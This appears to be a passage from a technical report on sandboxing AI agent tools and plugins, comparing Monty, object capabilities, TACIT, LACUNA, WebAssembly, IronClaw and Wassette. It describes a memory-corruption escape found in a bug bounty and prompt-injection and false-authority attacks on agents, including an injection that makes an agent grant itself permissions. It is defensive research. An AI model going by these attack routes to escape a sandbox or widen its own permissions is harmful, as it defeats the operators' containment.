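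Many file sandboxes check a path as text and then open it, which can fail if someone swaps a folder for a link between the two steps. Monty's file code opens the mounted folder once, keeps the handle, and performs every later operation relative to it, using a library that cannot follow `..` or a symbolic link out of the folder. Pydantic's *Worker execution (monty subprocess, monty-pool, Monty/AsyncMonty)* explains that the mount stays attached to the original folder even if a program renames it. The file code also rejects pipes and devices, because reading one could block the framework indefinitely.

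The framework can give the program one of the framework's own objects in a wrapper that lists the permitted attributes and methods. Both lists are empty by default. In Pydantic's example, a program may read a bank account's owner and balance and call `withdraw`, but it cannot call `close`. If a permitted method returns another object, Monty does not pass it on unless the developer has chosen a wrapper for that object too. This blocks the kind of attack that defeated the filters, where code used a harmless object to reach a more powerful one. The permitted methods, like host functions, still run with all the framework's authority.

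Resource limits can stop programs that never finish or that fill up memory, but the main time and memory limits are off by default. The time limit counts only the interpreter's own work, not host calls, so a program could spend hours making slow calls without reaching it. A separate limit on how many times the program can pause for host calls restricts this. The time limits also reset with each new piece of code in a session, and Pydantic leaves it to the framework to limit the total time. Willison (2026) had Claude Code examine Monty in May and found that its limits on time, memory, allocations and recursion appeared to work as advertised.

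Monty's main drawback is that it lacks much of Python. Programs cannot install third-party packages or use much of the standard library, and classes cannot extend built-in types. Pydantic recommends a container or virtual machine for coding agents that need build tools and packages. Pydantic is also steadily adding features to Monty because models write code that uses them. The first release did not support classes. Each addition makes the interpreter more useful but gives attackers more code to search for bugs.

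### Three rounds of public attacks

In April 2026, Pydantic tested Monty by putting up a server that ran anyone's Python code with no other protection. Pydantic offered $5,000 to the first person to read a secret from either a file or an environment variable. It reports that the server received almost 1.5 million requests from about 650 IP addresses, and that Owen Kwan of the security company Veria Labs found the secret in less than 48 hours.

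Kwan found a flaw in how Monty managed memory, unlike attackers of filters, who find names missing from a list. Rust's compiler normally prevents such flaws by allowing either many parts of a program to read a value or one part to change it, but never both at once. This rule is awkward for a Python interpreter, whose objects refer to each other freely. Applied directly, it would stop Monty from reading one list while adding its items to another. Rust has standard ways around this, but Pydantic wanted to avoid their run-time overhead and complexity. It wrote its own solution in `unsafe` Rust, where the programmer takes over some of the compiler's responsibility for memory safety. The solution was correct only under certain conditions, including that an object never changes its type.

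Monty's garbage collector, which frees memory that a program has stopped using, broke that condition. It starts from a set of objects known to be in use, follows their references, and frees whatever it cannot reach. The developers had not included lists that were being sorted in the starting set. The collector could therefore free a list mid-sort, and an object of a different type, with contents chosen by the attacker, could take its place. Attackers commonly use this kind of error, called a use-after-free, to make a program run their native code.

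Pydantic fixed the flaw in version 0.0.16 by adding the missing objects to the starting set, and checked its `unsafe` code again. It estimates that without the `unsafe` code, the collector's mistake would almost certainly have caused only crashes or wrong results. This is probably right, but inspecting the `unsafe` code alone is not enough, because the collector's ordinary code broke a condition that the `unsafe` code needed. Pydantic admitted afterwards that the collector's design still did not rule out a similar omission elsewhere.

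The contest also exposed a mistake on the host's side. Someone wrote to a fake secret file, and others who read it thought they had won. Pydantic blamed a file-access helper whose interface was so confusing that its own author had misused it. Stanislav Fort of the security company AISLE received $300 for being the first to report a weakness in the server's virtual file system.

The second round began at the end of May with a $10,000 prize, paid by Pydantic, Hugging Face and Prefect, the company behind a tool-server framework that runs Monty by default. According to Pydantic's *Hack Monty Round 3 & Round 2 results*, nobody escaped or read a secret, though entrants reported crashes and problems with resource limits. The third round ran through August with a prize of up to $20,000, and Pydantic also offered money for escaping a mounted folder or crashing the server. Pydantic has since mentioned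 the round in its marketing without giving a result. It released version 1 in the autumn, but this is little evidence of the outcome, because it also kept releasing new versions after the successful attack in April.

Two months without an escape is encouraging, given how quickly the first attack succeeded, but it is limited evidence. Many of the 1.5 million requests in the first round may have been near-copies, and one good idea was enough to succeed. The contests also tested the interpreter with Pydantic's own server around it, so they cannot show whether another developer's host functions are safe.

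### The move to worker processes

Until mid-2026, Monty normally ran inside the framework's process. In Pydantic's announcement of the second round, Prefect said, "Embedded also means a sandbox escape is a host compromise." After an escape like Kwan's, the attacker's native code would run in the same address space as every key in the framework. Even a simple crash in the interpreter would bring down the whole agent.

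By August, Pydantic had moved Monty into worker processes for its Python package and for its JavaScript package on servers. The framework starts a pool of workers and assigns one to each session. Pydantic (2026) gives crashes as the main reason, saying that no Monty process can be made fully crash-proof because hostile input can exhaust the stack or make a memory allocation fail. When a worker crashes, the pool replaces it and the framework keeps running. A separate process also makes it possible to measure memory accurately and to kill a program that gets past the interpreter's own time limit.

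The workers also start with no environment variables, so keys stored there never enter their memory. This would have protected the environment variable that Kwan read. But a worker runs on the same machine as the application and with the same operating-system privileges, as Pydantic acknowledges in its *Comparison to Alternatives*. An attacker who escaped into the worker could probably still read the other secret, which was in a file, unless the operator had restricted the worker further.

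The framework also treats every message from a worker as untrusted, since an attacker may control the worker. It limits the memory that a decoded message can occupy and discards a worker that breaks the protocol. By default, however, a worker serves up to 1,000 sessions before the pool replaces it, so an attacker who takes one over might see data from later sessions. When callers do not trust each other, Pydantic's *Pools* recommends a setting that gives each session a new process.

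The move made Monty slower to start. The early version could run a tiny program inside an existing process in about 0.004 milliseconds. Getting a session from an open pool and running `1 + 1` now takes 0.8 milliseconds, roughly 200 times as long, although the two tests were not identical. It takes 5 milliseconds if the framework has to create the pool first. Nobody would notice the difference in an agent that waits seconds for each model reply.

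The table gives Pydantic's own measurements, in milliseconds. Pydantic took most of them in September 2026 on an Apple M3 Max computer. "Ten commands" is the time to run a short series of commands in a sandbox that already exists.

| Sandbox | New sandbox | Ten commands | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Monty, open pool | 0.8 | 0.4 | 1.2 |
| Monty, new pool | 5 | 0.4 | 5 |
| Monty on Pydantic's commercial server | 2 | 5 | 7 |
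| Standard Python in WebAssembly (wasmtime) | 16 | 180 | 200 |
| Docker container | 195 | 700 | 900 |
| Remote sandbox service (Daytona) | 1,500 | 400 | 1,900 |
| Pyodide in the Deno runtime | 2,700 | 35 | 2,700 |

The comparison favours Monty in two ways. Monty's best figure uses a worker that is already running, while the containers and other sandboxes start from nothing, although a developer could keep a pool of those ready too. Monty also keeps its state between commands, whereas the test made most of the alternatives rerun every earlier command before each new one. Daytona advertises a start time below 90 milliseconds, which Pydantic could not reproduce. Monty would probably still be much faster than starting a container, because it has far less to load.

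Rust developers can still run Monty inside the calling process by using the `monty` crate (a Rust package). Docs.rs' *monty 0.0.21*, the documentation for an earlier version, presents this as an advantage over containers because the interpreter starts in microseconds. The interpreter still gives the program no file or network access of its own, but if it crashes, the framework crashes too, and an attacker who exploits a memory error gets direct access to the framework's keys. Pydantic therefore recommends a different crate, `monty-pool`, which uses worker processes. In a web browser, where Monty can't use separate processes, it runs as WebAssembly in a background thread, and a crash of the JavaScript engine can still affect the page that started Monty.

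## Object capabilities and authority tracked by types

A program running in Monty can call only the functions the framework supplies, but it usually passes a string, such as a folder name, to identify what a function should act on. The function then looks up that name with all the framework's authority, as Hardy's compiler did with the name of the billing file. In an object-capability language, the caller instead passes a reference, a value that points to an object such as a list, an open file or a mail client. References are the only permissions in such a language, so code cannot use an object without a reference to it.

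### Four ways to get a reference

Miller (2006), in *Robust Composition*, lists the only four ways in which one object can come to hold a reference to another. In the mail assistant they look like this:

- Initial conditions: the framework starts up already holding a mail client, which contains the mail token.
- Parenthood: the framework creates a handle for one mail folder, and at that moment nothing else has a reference to it.
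- Endowment: the framework creates the summariser with that handle already built in.
- Introduction: the framework, which has references to both the summariser and the handle, passes the handle to the summariser as an argument in a call.

No program can forge a reference by guessing an address or a name. Miller sums up the consequence as "only connectivity begets connectivity". If no reference links two groups of objects, no sequence of calls will link them. If a few objects sit between the groups, everything that passes from one group to the other must go through those objects. A reviewer can read their code closely and assume that the plugin is malicious.

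Nobody can work out exactly what the summariser will eventually be able to do, because that depends on how all the programs involved behave. Miller therefore uses upper bounds. The simplest bound follows the references and ignores what the code does. It is safe but pessimistic, because the handle refers to the mail client, which can send mail, so under this bound the summariser might be able to send mail too. A tighter bound also takes the handle's code into account. If that code only searches and reads one folder, the summariser can do no more than that to the mailbox.

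Anyone who learns or guesses a string or number has it. Miller's examples are the number 7 and a private key. The mail token is a string, so a plugin that saw it could write it into a summary. A handle has no written form that would work elsewhere, which is a good reason to give the plugin a handle and keep the token in the framework.

### A read-only mailbox that the framework can withdraw

The following pseudocode is close to JavaScript. The object `mail` holds the token and can read, send and delete anything in the account.

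```js
function readOnlyFolder(mail, folder) {
  return {
    search(words) { return mail.search(folder, words); },
    read(id)      { return mail.read(folder, id); }
  };
}

function makeRevocable(target) {
  let current = target;
  return {
    handle: {
      search(words) { return current.search(words); },
      read(id)      { return current.read(id); }
    },
    revoke() { current = null; }
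  };
}

const { handle, revoke } =
  makeRevocable(readOnlyFolder(mail, "Landlord"));
const summary = summariser.run(handle);
revoke();
```

`readOnlyFolder` is an example of attenuation, which means making a weaker capability from a stronger one. It returns an object with two functions that can use `mail` because they keep access to the variables that surrounded them when they were created. A caller cannot access those variables directly, so the summariser cannot send mail, change the folder or read the token.

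`makeRevocable` adds a wrapper that forwards each call to whatever `current` refers to. `revoke` empties that variable, so later calls fail even if the summariser has saved the handle or given it to another plugin. Programmers call this wrapper a caretaker, and *Robust and Compositional Verification of Object Capability Patterns* (Swasey, Garg and Dreyer, 2017) gives machine-checked proofs about it.

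Revocation cannot take back letters the summariser has already read, and it may not affect objects obtained through the handle. If `read` returned a live message object with its own `reply` function, the summariser could keep using that object after the call to `revoke`. To prevent this, the framework should return plain text or use a membrane, which is a caretaker that also wraps every object passing through it.

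The wrapper's own code can still be a confused deputy. Suppose the mail provider treats `in:anywhere` in a search as a command to search the whole account. The summariser could then read other folders through `search`, unless the wrapper or the mail client removed such commands. `read` must also check that the message number belongs to the permitted folder. A reviewer has a fair chance of finding mistakes like these because the privileged code is only a dozen lines long.

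### What a language has to give up

Most object-oriented languages already use references in roughly this way. To make references the only source of authority, Miller and Shapiro mainly take features away:

- Forgeable references. A C++ program can turn an integer into a pointer and so reach any object whose address it can guess. (CHERI processors can prevent this in hardware.)
- Direct access to another object's private data. With it, the summariser could pull `mail` out of the handle.
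- Global variables that programs can change. Java and Smalltalk have them, and two plugins could use one to exchange references without anyone introducing them.
- Powerful globals. In an ordinary JavaScript runtime on a server, any module can import functions that open files.
- Unchecked reflection, which made the escapes from Python filters possible.

Miller and Shapiro note that good object-oriented style already follows these rules. This helps developers of new code more than users of old libraries.

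The rules also do little to keep a program running. Miller designed his language, E, to keep an object's data consistent when its callers misbehave, but a hostile caller may still stop the object from making progress, for instance by using up memory.

### Hardened JavaScript

OpenClaw's plugins are JavaScript or TypeScript modules, so Hardened JavaScript, a proposed addition to the language standard, is the most practical version of this approach for them. The `ses` package provides it on existing JavaScript engines. *SES*, the package's documentation, describes three main parts.

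The first is `lockdown()`, which freezes the built-in objects that all code in the program shares, including those that supply the methods of arrays and functions. Otherwise, a plugin could replace a standard array method with one that also copies the array's contents, and the framework would run the plugin's version on its own data.

The second part, `harden()`, freezes an object and everything reachable through its properties. The framework should harden the mailbox handle before sharing it, so that one plugin cannot swap the `search` function for a fake and deceive another. Hardening does not freeze variables inside functions, so `revoke` still works.

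The third part is the compartment, an environment with its own global variables. A compartment starts with the standard language features but without functions such as `fetch`, which makes network requests. The current time and random numbers are also missing by default, because programs could use them to communicate covertly. The framework could load the summariser like this:

```js
lockdown();
const box = new Compartment({
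  globals: { mailbox: harden(handle) },
  __options__: true   // temporary compatibility setting
});
box.evaluate(summariserSource);
```

Compartments also guard against the kind of inherited link that defeated Cohere's Terrarium. In ordinary JavaScript, a program can follow links from almost any function to `Function`, which turns text into code that can use the surrounding global variables. `lockdown()` replaces the shared link with a dummy that only raises an error. Each compartment has its own `Function`, and code made with it can use only that compartment's globals.

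The cryptocurrency wallet MetaMask and the smart-contract company Agoric use Hardened JavaScript in production, partly to confine third-party plugins. Endo, a platform built on Hardened JavaScript, demonstrates a confined plugin system. According to Endo's documentation, most libraries written for Node.js, the usual JavaScript runtime on servers, work without modification because few of them alter shared objects. But a plugin that reads files would still fail until the framework gave it file access, so someone has to decide how much access to give.

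`lockdown()` takes no powers away from code outside compartments, including plugins the framework loads normally. A compartment also shares the framework's process, so a memory error in the JavaScript engine can expose the token, as with an embedded Monty, and an endless loop in a plugin can stall the whole agent. I therefore think Hardened JavaScript is a good way to divide authority among semi-trusted plugins but a weaker defence against a skilled attacker.

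### How TACIT uses types

A handle limits which calls a component can make, but not what the component does with the results. For example, a component with one handle for reading letters and another for web searches can leak a letter by passing its text from the first call to the second, even though each call is allowed.

In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) try to catch such leaks before the program runs. In their system, TACIT, the model writes its actions in Scala 3, which Odersky designed. They assume that the cloud model running the agent may be fully cooperating with an attacker.

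TACIT relies on an experimental Scala feature called capture checking. A type is the compiler's description of a value, such as "string" or "function from strings to numbers". Capture checking adds a capture set to the type, which lists the capabilities the value might use. For example, a function that takes a string, writes it to the file `f` and returns nothing has the type `String ->{f} Unit`. The type `String -> Unit` has an empty capture set, so a function of this type is pure, meaning it can't write to a file, send a request or cause any other outside effect. The compiler works out most capture sets itself. A set must include every capability the function uses, and may include some it doesn't use.

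This makes it possible to protect private data with a wrapper called `Classified`. Its most important method is:

```scala
def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The wrapper applies the caller's function `f` to the hidden data and wraps the result. Because `f` must be pure, it can shorten or search a letter but cannot send it anywhere. The agent's code has no method for unwrapping the data.

Capture sets also control how long a capability lasts. To access files, a snippet (a short program from the model) calls `requestFileSystem` with a folder and a block of code. Inside the block, the snippet has a file-system capability for that folder. The type of the block's result may not refer to the capability, so the compiler rejects a snippet that returns an open file or a function that would open one later. This check stops a handle from leaving the block, whereas the caretaker in the earlier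 example cuts off a leaked handle when someone calls `revoke`.

This protection would fail if a snippet could use a capability without the compiler tracking it. Safe mode, a restricted form of Scala, therefore forbids unchecked type conversions, reflection, and annotations that turn off checks. It also blocks global functions unless they are safe. Unlike older object-capability languages, TACIT can allow powerful global objects, because a function's type shows any use of them.

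A snippet goes through these steps:

1. The agent sends it to TACIT through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools. The agent itself can be written in any language.
2. TACIT compiles the whole snippet in safe mode. If any part fails, none of it runs, and the compiler's errors go back to the model.
3. If the snippet compiles, TACIT runs it. The library still checks some things at this stage, such as whether a file path lies inside the requested folder.
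4. Ordinary output goes to both the agent and the user. For wrapped data, the agent sees only `Classified(****)`, while the user's terminal shows the text.

Wrapped values stay wrapped in later turns of the conversation. Error messages could also reveal private text, so TACIT turns errors into ordinary values that the wrapper can hide.

### One accepted and one rejected snippet

Suppose that the landlord's letter is in a folder the user has marked as classified. The agent's model may not see it, but a trusted model on the user's own computer may. The following snippet compiles:

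```scala
val summary = requestFileSystem("/mail") {
  val letter = readClassified("/mail/private/landlord.txt")
  chat(letter.map(text => s"Summarise this letter: $text"))
}
println(summary)
```

`readClassified` returns the letter in a wrapper. The function passed to `map` only joins two pieces of text, so its capture set is empty. `chat` sends the wrapped prompt to the trusted model and returns a wrapped answer. The block's result contains no file capability, so it may leave the block. The user sees the summary, while the agent gets asterisks in its place.

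This version does not compile:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/mail") {
  val letter = readClassified("/mail/private/landlord.txt")
  letter.map { text => println(text) }
}
```

Printing needs an input/output capability, `io`, so the function's type is `String ->{io} Unit`, but `map` requires `String -> Unit`. The compiler reports that the capability cannot flow into an empty capture set, so the program never opens the letter. In their tests, Odersky and colleagues found an agent attempting the same thing with a GitHub key instead of the letter.

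### How well TACIT worked

To test for leaks, Odersky and colleagues built a sample software project with a folder of API keys, confidential documents and a database. They paired each of 12 legitimate tasks with each of 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials, and added 11 requests in which the user tried to get the secrets directly or by posing as someone with authority. They ran all 131 trials with both Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5, and counted a leak whenever secret content appeared in the agent's output.

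Neither model leaked anything with the wrapper. Without it, Claude leaked secrets in 2 trials, both involving a false claim of authority, and MiniMax in 11. The wrapper did not make the agents less useful. Claude completed 99.2% of the legitimate tasks with the wrapper and 83.3% without it, while MiniMax completed 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. Odersky and colleagues suggest that Claude scored lower without the wrapper partly because it ran out of time and stopped to warn the user about injections.

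The perfect security score is mainly evidence that the implementation works as designed, since the design keeps the secret text away from the agent's model. The score also depended on the secrets being in a folder the researchers had marked in advance. A key left in an ordinary configuration file would have reached the model as plain text.

They also adapted AgentDojo, a prompt-injection benchmark with simulated banking, office, Slack and travel tasks. Only one attack succeeded in 963 trials with each of two models, and it was arguably harmless. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted reviews to the user, including a planted recommendation for another hotel. The agent's instructions for this test included a warning that side effects inside `map` would happen immediately. This suggests that some of the adapted tools did not count as effects, in which case much of the protection may have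 come from hiding untrusted text from the agent's model.

A separate set of tests measured whether writing Scala makes agents worse at their work. In the customer-service benchmark τ²-bench, three models solved 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points more tasks with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls. For example, MiniMax improved from 75.1% to 77.5% on retail tasks. Its score on SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software bugs, dropped from 43.3% to 41.7%. At most 8% of the snippets in τ²-bench needed a retry after a compiler error, and compiling usually took less than a second.

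These results show that models can write typed Scala, even though their training data contains little of it. They are weaker evidence about capabilities, because the airline and retail functions listed in the paper have no capabilities in their signatures. Some of the improvement may come from letting the model write programs, which also helped in Pydantic's tests of code mode.

### What LACUNA changes

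In TACIT, a conventional agent loop sends snippets to a separate tool. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a later system from the same group, instead puts the model call inside the program. A developer writes `agent[T](task)` wherever the program needs a value of type `T`. When execution reaches that call, the model writes code to produce the value, and the compiler checks the code as if the developer had typed it there. The code may contain further `agent` calls, so the model can create its own loops and sub-agents.

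The variables available at that point are the agent's permissions. If the developer gives one part of the program a file handle and another part a network handle, code generated in the first part can read files but cannot send them anywhere. As in TACIT, a rejected snippet has no partial effects. In one example, the model writes code that subtracts 50 from a balance and then returns text where the program expects a number. The compiler rejects both lines, so the balance stays at 100.

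LACUNA also makes wrapped data more useful. In TACIT, the cloud model has to write the function for `map` without seeing the data. In LACUNA, that function can call a trusted local model, which reads the letter and writes code suited to it. The compiler checks this code too, and the code must also be pure.

The extra flexibility seems to make tasks harder for the model. On τ²-bench, DeepSeek-V4-Flash solved 76.0% of 392 tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls. That 14-percentage-point gap is large, though Zhao and colleagues describe the results as on par. On the telecom tasks, the compiler rejected 89% of the code from the smaller Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite. Zhao and colleagues chose cheaper models, and stronger ones would probably do better.

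The next table compares the systems on AgentDojo, including CaMeL, an earlier system that tracks the origin of data at runtime. The percentages are the share of legitimate tasks each system completed.

| Model and tasks | CaMeL | TACIT | LACUNA |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 63.2% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, office | 53.8% | 50.5% | 56.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, Slack | 48.6% | 40.0% | 42.9% |
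| Gemini 2.5 Pro, travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 63.6% |
| o4-mini-high, banking | 62.5% | 59.0% | 66.0% |
| o4-mini-high, office | 81.4% | 52.9% | 55.5% |
| o4-mini-high, Slack | 68.6% | 47.6% | 49.5% |
| o4-mini-high, travel | 74.3% | 68.6% | 71.4% |
| Successful attacks, all tasks | 1 | 1 | 8 |

Odersky and colleagues call TACIT's usefulness comparable to CaMeL's. This is fair for most of the Gemini results, but with o4-mini-high, TACIT completed far fewer office and Slack tasks than CaMeL. Attacks on LACUNA succeeded in eight of about 1,900 trials. This is consistent with Zhao and colleagues' acknowledgment that the compiler cannot stop an attacker from getting the model to misuse a capability that the task needs.

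### What the guarantee depends on

TACIT's trusted computing base includes the Scala compiler, the program that runs the compiled code, and TACIT's library. Library developers can also mark a module `@assumeSafe`, which exempts it from safe mode. Odersky and colleagues give the example of a cache of results from earlier calls. Its developer must make sure the cache holds nothing else, because the compiler no longer checks. Users must also trust the `chat` function, which sends text to another model even though its type lists no capabilities. They rely on the operator's promise that this model keeps nothing and has no tools.

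Odersky and colleagues reply that the basic type system has machine-checked proofs, though safe mode still lacks a full proof. They recommend also running TACIT inside a sandbox in case someone breaks out of the language runtime. Their guarantee does not cover side channels such as timing.

A capability that is too broad protects very little. In TACIT's interface, the snippet itself specifies the folder, websites or commands it requests, so something else has to limit its access. Commands are especially risky because they run outside Scala. An example in the TACIT library's documentation requests permission to run `python`, and a Python program can read a classified file without any wrapper. Odersky and colleagues accept that the protection is then only as good as the list of permitted commands, and advise limiting the list to specific, safe ones such as `git diff`. Zhao and colleagues similarly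 leave the developer to keep each agent's permissions narrow.

The most practical objection is the amount of rewriting. Odersky and colleagues answer that the reusable part of TACIT is about 1,000 lines, and that describing the tools for a new domain takes a few hundred more, which an agent can help write. This is a reasonable answer for tools and model-written code, but not for an existing plugin such as the summariser, which someone would have to rewrite in Scala or run as an outside program that the compiler cannot check. Hardened JavaScript requires fewer changes to such a plugin, but it cannot check that a function is pure.

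A framework can also keep its current language and store capabilities as records that it checks at each call. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) describes a Python system that does this. Each record names a resource and the permitted operations, and an agent can pass on the same rights or fewer. Showing the model a new tool gives it no new rights over existing resources. In Zhang's main evaluation, none of 119 checks found an unauthorised effect. But the records limit only calls that go through the system, and Zhang counts the Python interpreter and any installed extension modules as trusted. A malicious extension in the same process could ignore or change the records.

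## Software fault isolation and WebAssembly

The permission records in Agent libOS and the references in Hardened JavaScript do not protect against native code that can write to any address in the process. Developers can move such code to another process, but in the early 1990s a call between processes often took 100 to 1,000 times as long as an ordinary function call. In *Efficient Software-Based Fault Isolation*, Wahbe, Lucco and colleagues (1993) showed how to confine the code within the same process. One of their test cases was the database POSTGRES, which loads C functions written by its users and could lose data if any of them had a bug.

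### Masking an address

In software fault isolation, the loader gives the component one region of memory for its code and another for its data. All addresses in a region have the same upper bits, called the segment identifier. A modified compiler finds every store or jump whose target it cannot determine in advance, such as a store through a pointer, and inserts two instructions before it. The first clears the upper bits of the target address, and the second sets them to the component's own segment identifier.

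Suppose that the summariser's data region runs from `0x2A000000` to `0x2AFFFFFF`. The first two hexadecimal digits are the segment identifier, and the other six give the position within the region. The framework keeps the mail token at `0x7F3451C8`, and the summariser tries to overwrite it:

```
target address          0x7F3451C8
AND with 0x00FFFFFF     0x003451C8
OR with  0x2A000000     0x2A3451C8
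```

The store writes to the summariser's own region and does not change the token. Both steps leave a legitimate address, such as `0x2A001000`, unchanged. Masking does not detect the bad store, so the summariser may keep running with damaged data. Wahbe and colleagues also describe a version that compares the upper bits and stops the component if they are wrong. This version helps developers find bugs but needs four instructions instead of two.

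A hostile component could try to jump straight to the store and skip the masking. The compiler therefore reserves a processor register for masked addresses, and every unsafe store must take its target from that register. The component's own code never changes the register, so the store still uses a valid address after a jump into the middle of the sequence. When the component loads, a verifier reads its machine code and rejects it if any store or jump breaks these rules, so the user has to trust the verifier but not the compiler.

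The component can leave its region only through a read-only table of permitted entry points into the rest of the program. The compiler replaces direct system calls with calls to trusted code, which decides whether each one is safe. Without this check, the component could close or delete files that the framework is using.

### Reads, writes and the price of a call

The basic version of software fault isolation checks stores and jumps but not reads, because Wahbe and colleagues mainly wanted to stop faulty modules from corrupting data. A summariser confined in this way could still read the mail token. On one of their two test machines, a DECstation, checking stores and jumps slowed programs by 4.3% on average, and checking reads as well raised the slowdown to 21.8%. An agent framework needs the slower version, since its components share an address space with keys.

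In return, calls became much cheaper. A call into a confined module took 1.1 microseconds on the DECstation, compared with 205 microseconds for a round trip between two processes through a pipe. Wahbe and colleagues estimate the overall benefit as

savings = (1 − *r*)*t*<sub>c</sub> − *h* *t*<sub>d</sub>

Here *t*<sub>c</sub> is the share of time the program would spend on calls between processes, and *t*<sub>d</sub> is the share it spends inside the component. The slowdown from the added checks is *h*, and *r* is the time a software-isolated call takes divided by the time a call between processes takes. One POSTGRES query made 1.4 million calls into user code. Software isolation slowed the query by 5.7%, while the researchers estimated that separate processes would have slowed it by 31.9%.

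The framework calls the summariser only once or twice per turn, so *t*<sub>c</sub> is close to zero and, by the formula, the checks take slightly more time than the technique saves. A better reason than speed to use the technique today is that a new sandbox needs only another region of memory, so a framework can create one for each call and then discard it.

### WebAssembly's memory and calls

WebAssembly applies software fault isolation to a portable bytecode. Developers compile C, Rust or another language to this bytecode, and a runtime translates it into machine code. The runtime checks types and stack operations before the program starts and checks memory bounds while it runs, as *Self-Hosted WebAssembly Runtime for Runtime-Neutral Checkpoint/Restore in Edge-Cloud Continuum* (2026) describes.

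A WebAssembly program's memory is one long array of bytes, called linear memory, and the program's addresses are indices into this array. *Segue & ColorGuard* (Narayan, Garfinkel and colleagues, 2022) explains that the runtime adds the array's starting address to the index at every load and store. The summariser therefore cannot refer to the mail token's location outside the array, even to read it.

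A WebAssembly program accesses memory by indexing into an array, and an index could point past the array's end. The runtime can compare each index with the array's current size, but this takes time. With the usual 32-bit indexes, it can instead reserve all the address space the program could reach and leave the unused part, called a guard region, unmapped. This takes about 8 GiB, because a load or store can add a fixed offset of up to 4 GiB to an index of up to 4 GiB. If the program touches the guard region, the processor raises a fault and the runtime stops the program. Masking would redirect the same access to another place in the program's memory.

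WebAssembly also restricts jumps. A function pointer is a number that selects an entry in a table, and before an indirect call through that pointer, the runtime checks that the entry exists and that the function has the expected parameter and result types. Return addresses sit on a call stack outside linear memory, which the program cannot write to. An attacker who overflows a buffer therefore cannot overwrite a return address to choose what runs next, as is often possible in an ordinary C program.

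A WebAssembly program has less protection inside its linear memory than a native program gets. *WADE* (2026), which proposes an attack detector for WebAssembly programs, notes that the runtime enforces only the memory's outer bounds. A C program's static data, heap and part of its stack lie in one writable block with no guard pages between them. A crafted attachment could therefore still corrupt the summariser and control what it returns. The attacker would also be able to call any function that the summariser may call.

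WebAssembly has no instruction for opening a file or sending a packet. A program can reach anything outside the sandbox only by calling functions that the framework supplies. It lists the functions it needs as imports, and the runtime will not start it if any are missing.

### Files and network access as grants

Most programs need operating system services, so the WebAssembly System Interface (WASI) defines standard imports for files, clocks, network connections and similar services. A WASI program opens a file relative to a directory handle it already holds, which avoids the ambient authority of the Unix function `open()`. The framework chooses the first handles when it starts the program. If it gives the summariser only a read-only handle for the attachments folder, the summariser has no call that would open the folder of login keys. The framework also chooses whether to supply network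 functions and which destinations they accept.

A basic WebAssembly module exchanges only numbers with the framework, so the two sides need a private convention for passing a string. The component model replaces this with declared types, and the runtime generates the code that copies text and records across the boundary. (A WebAssembly "component" is a module packaged in this way, which is narrower than this report's use of the word.) The developer also writes a "world", a declaration of everything the program may import and must provide. In an early version of IronClaw, the security-focused agent that Pirch and colleagues tested, the world for tools is only a few lines long:

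```wit
world sandboxed-tool {
    import host;
    export tool;
}
```

The `host` interface contains six functions, which write a log message, return the time, read a workspace file, make a web request, call another tool, and check whether a named secret exists. A reviewer can read this one file to find an upper bound, in Miller's sense, on what any tool can do, provided the runtime has no bugs.

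### IronClaw's tool runtime

IronClaw runs these tools in Wasmtime, the Bytecode Alliance's WebAssembly runtime. According to its documentation, IronClaw compiles each tool once, at registration, and checks the file's hash each time it loads the tool. Every call gets a fresh instance, so a tool cannot keep a letter in memory until the next call. Each instance has 10 MB of memory by default and a budget of "fuel" that it uses up as it executes instructions. IronClaw discards any instance that faults.

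By default, a tool has no access to files, the network or other tools. Its developer lists what it needs in a capabilities file. IronClaw handles a web request from a tool in these steps:

1. The tool calls the request function with a web address and no credential.
2. The host checks the address against the hosts and paths the tool may contact.
3. It scans the request for secrets that the tool may be trying to send out.
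4. It adds the credential and sends the request.
5. It scans the response for secrets and returns it to the tool.

A mail-search tool can therefore use the mail token without having it in its memory. The tool still has whatever authority the token gives it at the permitted addresses. If the allowed path covers both searching and sending, a malicious tool can send mail. The scans check for leaked credentials and may not detect a sentence from the landlord's letter, so a narrow list of permitted addresses probably matters more than the scans.

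Some of the tools available to an IronClaw agent run outside WebAssembly, on servers that use the Model Context Protocol (MCP). IronClaw's developer guide describes these servers as external processes with full system access and no sandbox. They manage their own credentials, and IronClaw cannot prevent them from leaking data. The guide recommends WebAssembly for tools that handle sensitive credentials, such as those for email or banking, but an MCP server where a good one already exists.

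This advice is practical because the WebAssembly tools have drawbacks. Developers must write them in Rust, the tools cannot hold a connection open in the background, and there is no large collection of them. But the model cannot tell the two kinds of tool apart, so it cannot prefer the confined one. An IronClaw user who installs mostly MCP servers gets little protection from the sandbox.

The attacks by Pirch and colleagues provide little evidence of how strong the sandbox is. All seven successful attacks on IronClaw came from people sending messages to the agent, not from malicious code in a WebAssembly tool.

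### Wassette

Microsoft's Wassette runs MCP tools in WebAssembly. It is an MCP server, so an existing agent can use it without changes. *Introducing Wassette* (2025) explains how an agent can fetch a component from an online registry and run it in Wasmtime. In the demonstration, a user asks GitHub Copilot to load a tool that fetches web pages. Copilot asks for confirmation before loading it. When the user requests a summary of a page, Copilot asks again before giving the tool access to that page's domain.

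In Wassette, each tool has its own policy and starts with no permissions. A sample policy in Microsoft's *What is Wassette?* allows a tool to read and write a workspace folder, read one configuration file, and contact one host. Wassette blocks everything else. Limiting a tool to one host prevents it from sending data to an arbitrary server, but a malicious tool could still leak data through a permitted host that accepts posts or uploads.

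The agent can change these policies. Wassette offers functions such as `grant-storage-permission` and `grant-network-permission` as ordinary MCP tools, and Microsoft recommends granting permissions by asking the agent in plain language. If a prompt injection causes the model to call one of these functions, only the confirmation prompt can prevent the change. Microsoft also says in its announcement that users may have to tell the model to "please fix the permission errors", which is a risky habit. An operator with sensitive files would do better to write the policy by hand and withhold the granting functions from the model.

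Wassette also protects secrets less well than IronClaw. A tool that needs an API key can receive it as an environment variable, which puts the key in the tool's own memory. Memory limits are planned but not yet available. The largest practical obstacle is that developers must rewrite existing MCP servers as WebAssembly components. Microsoft warns on the project page that Wassette is in early development and not ready for production.

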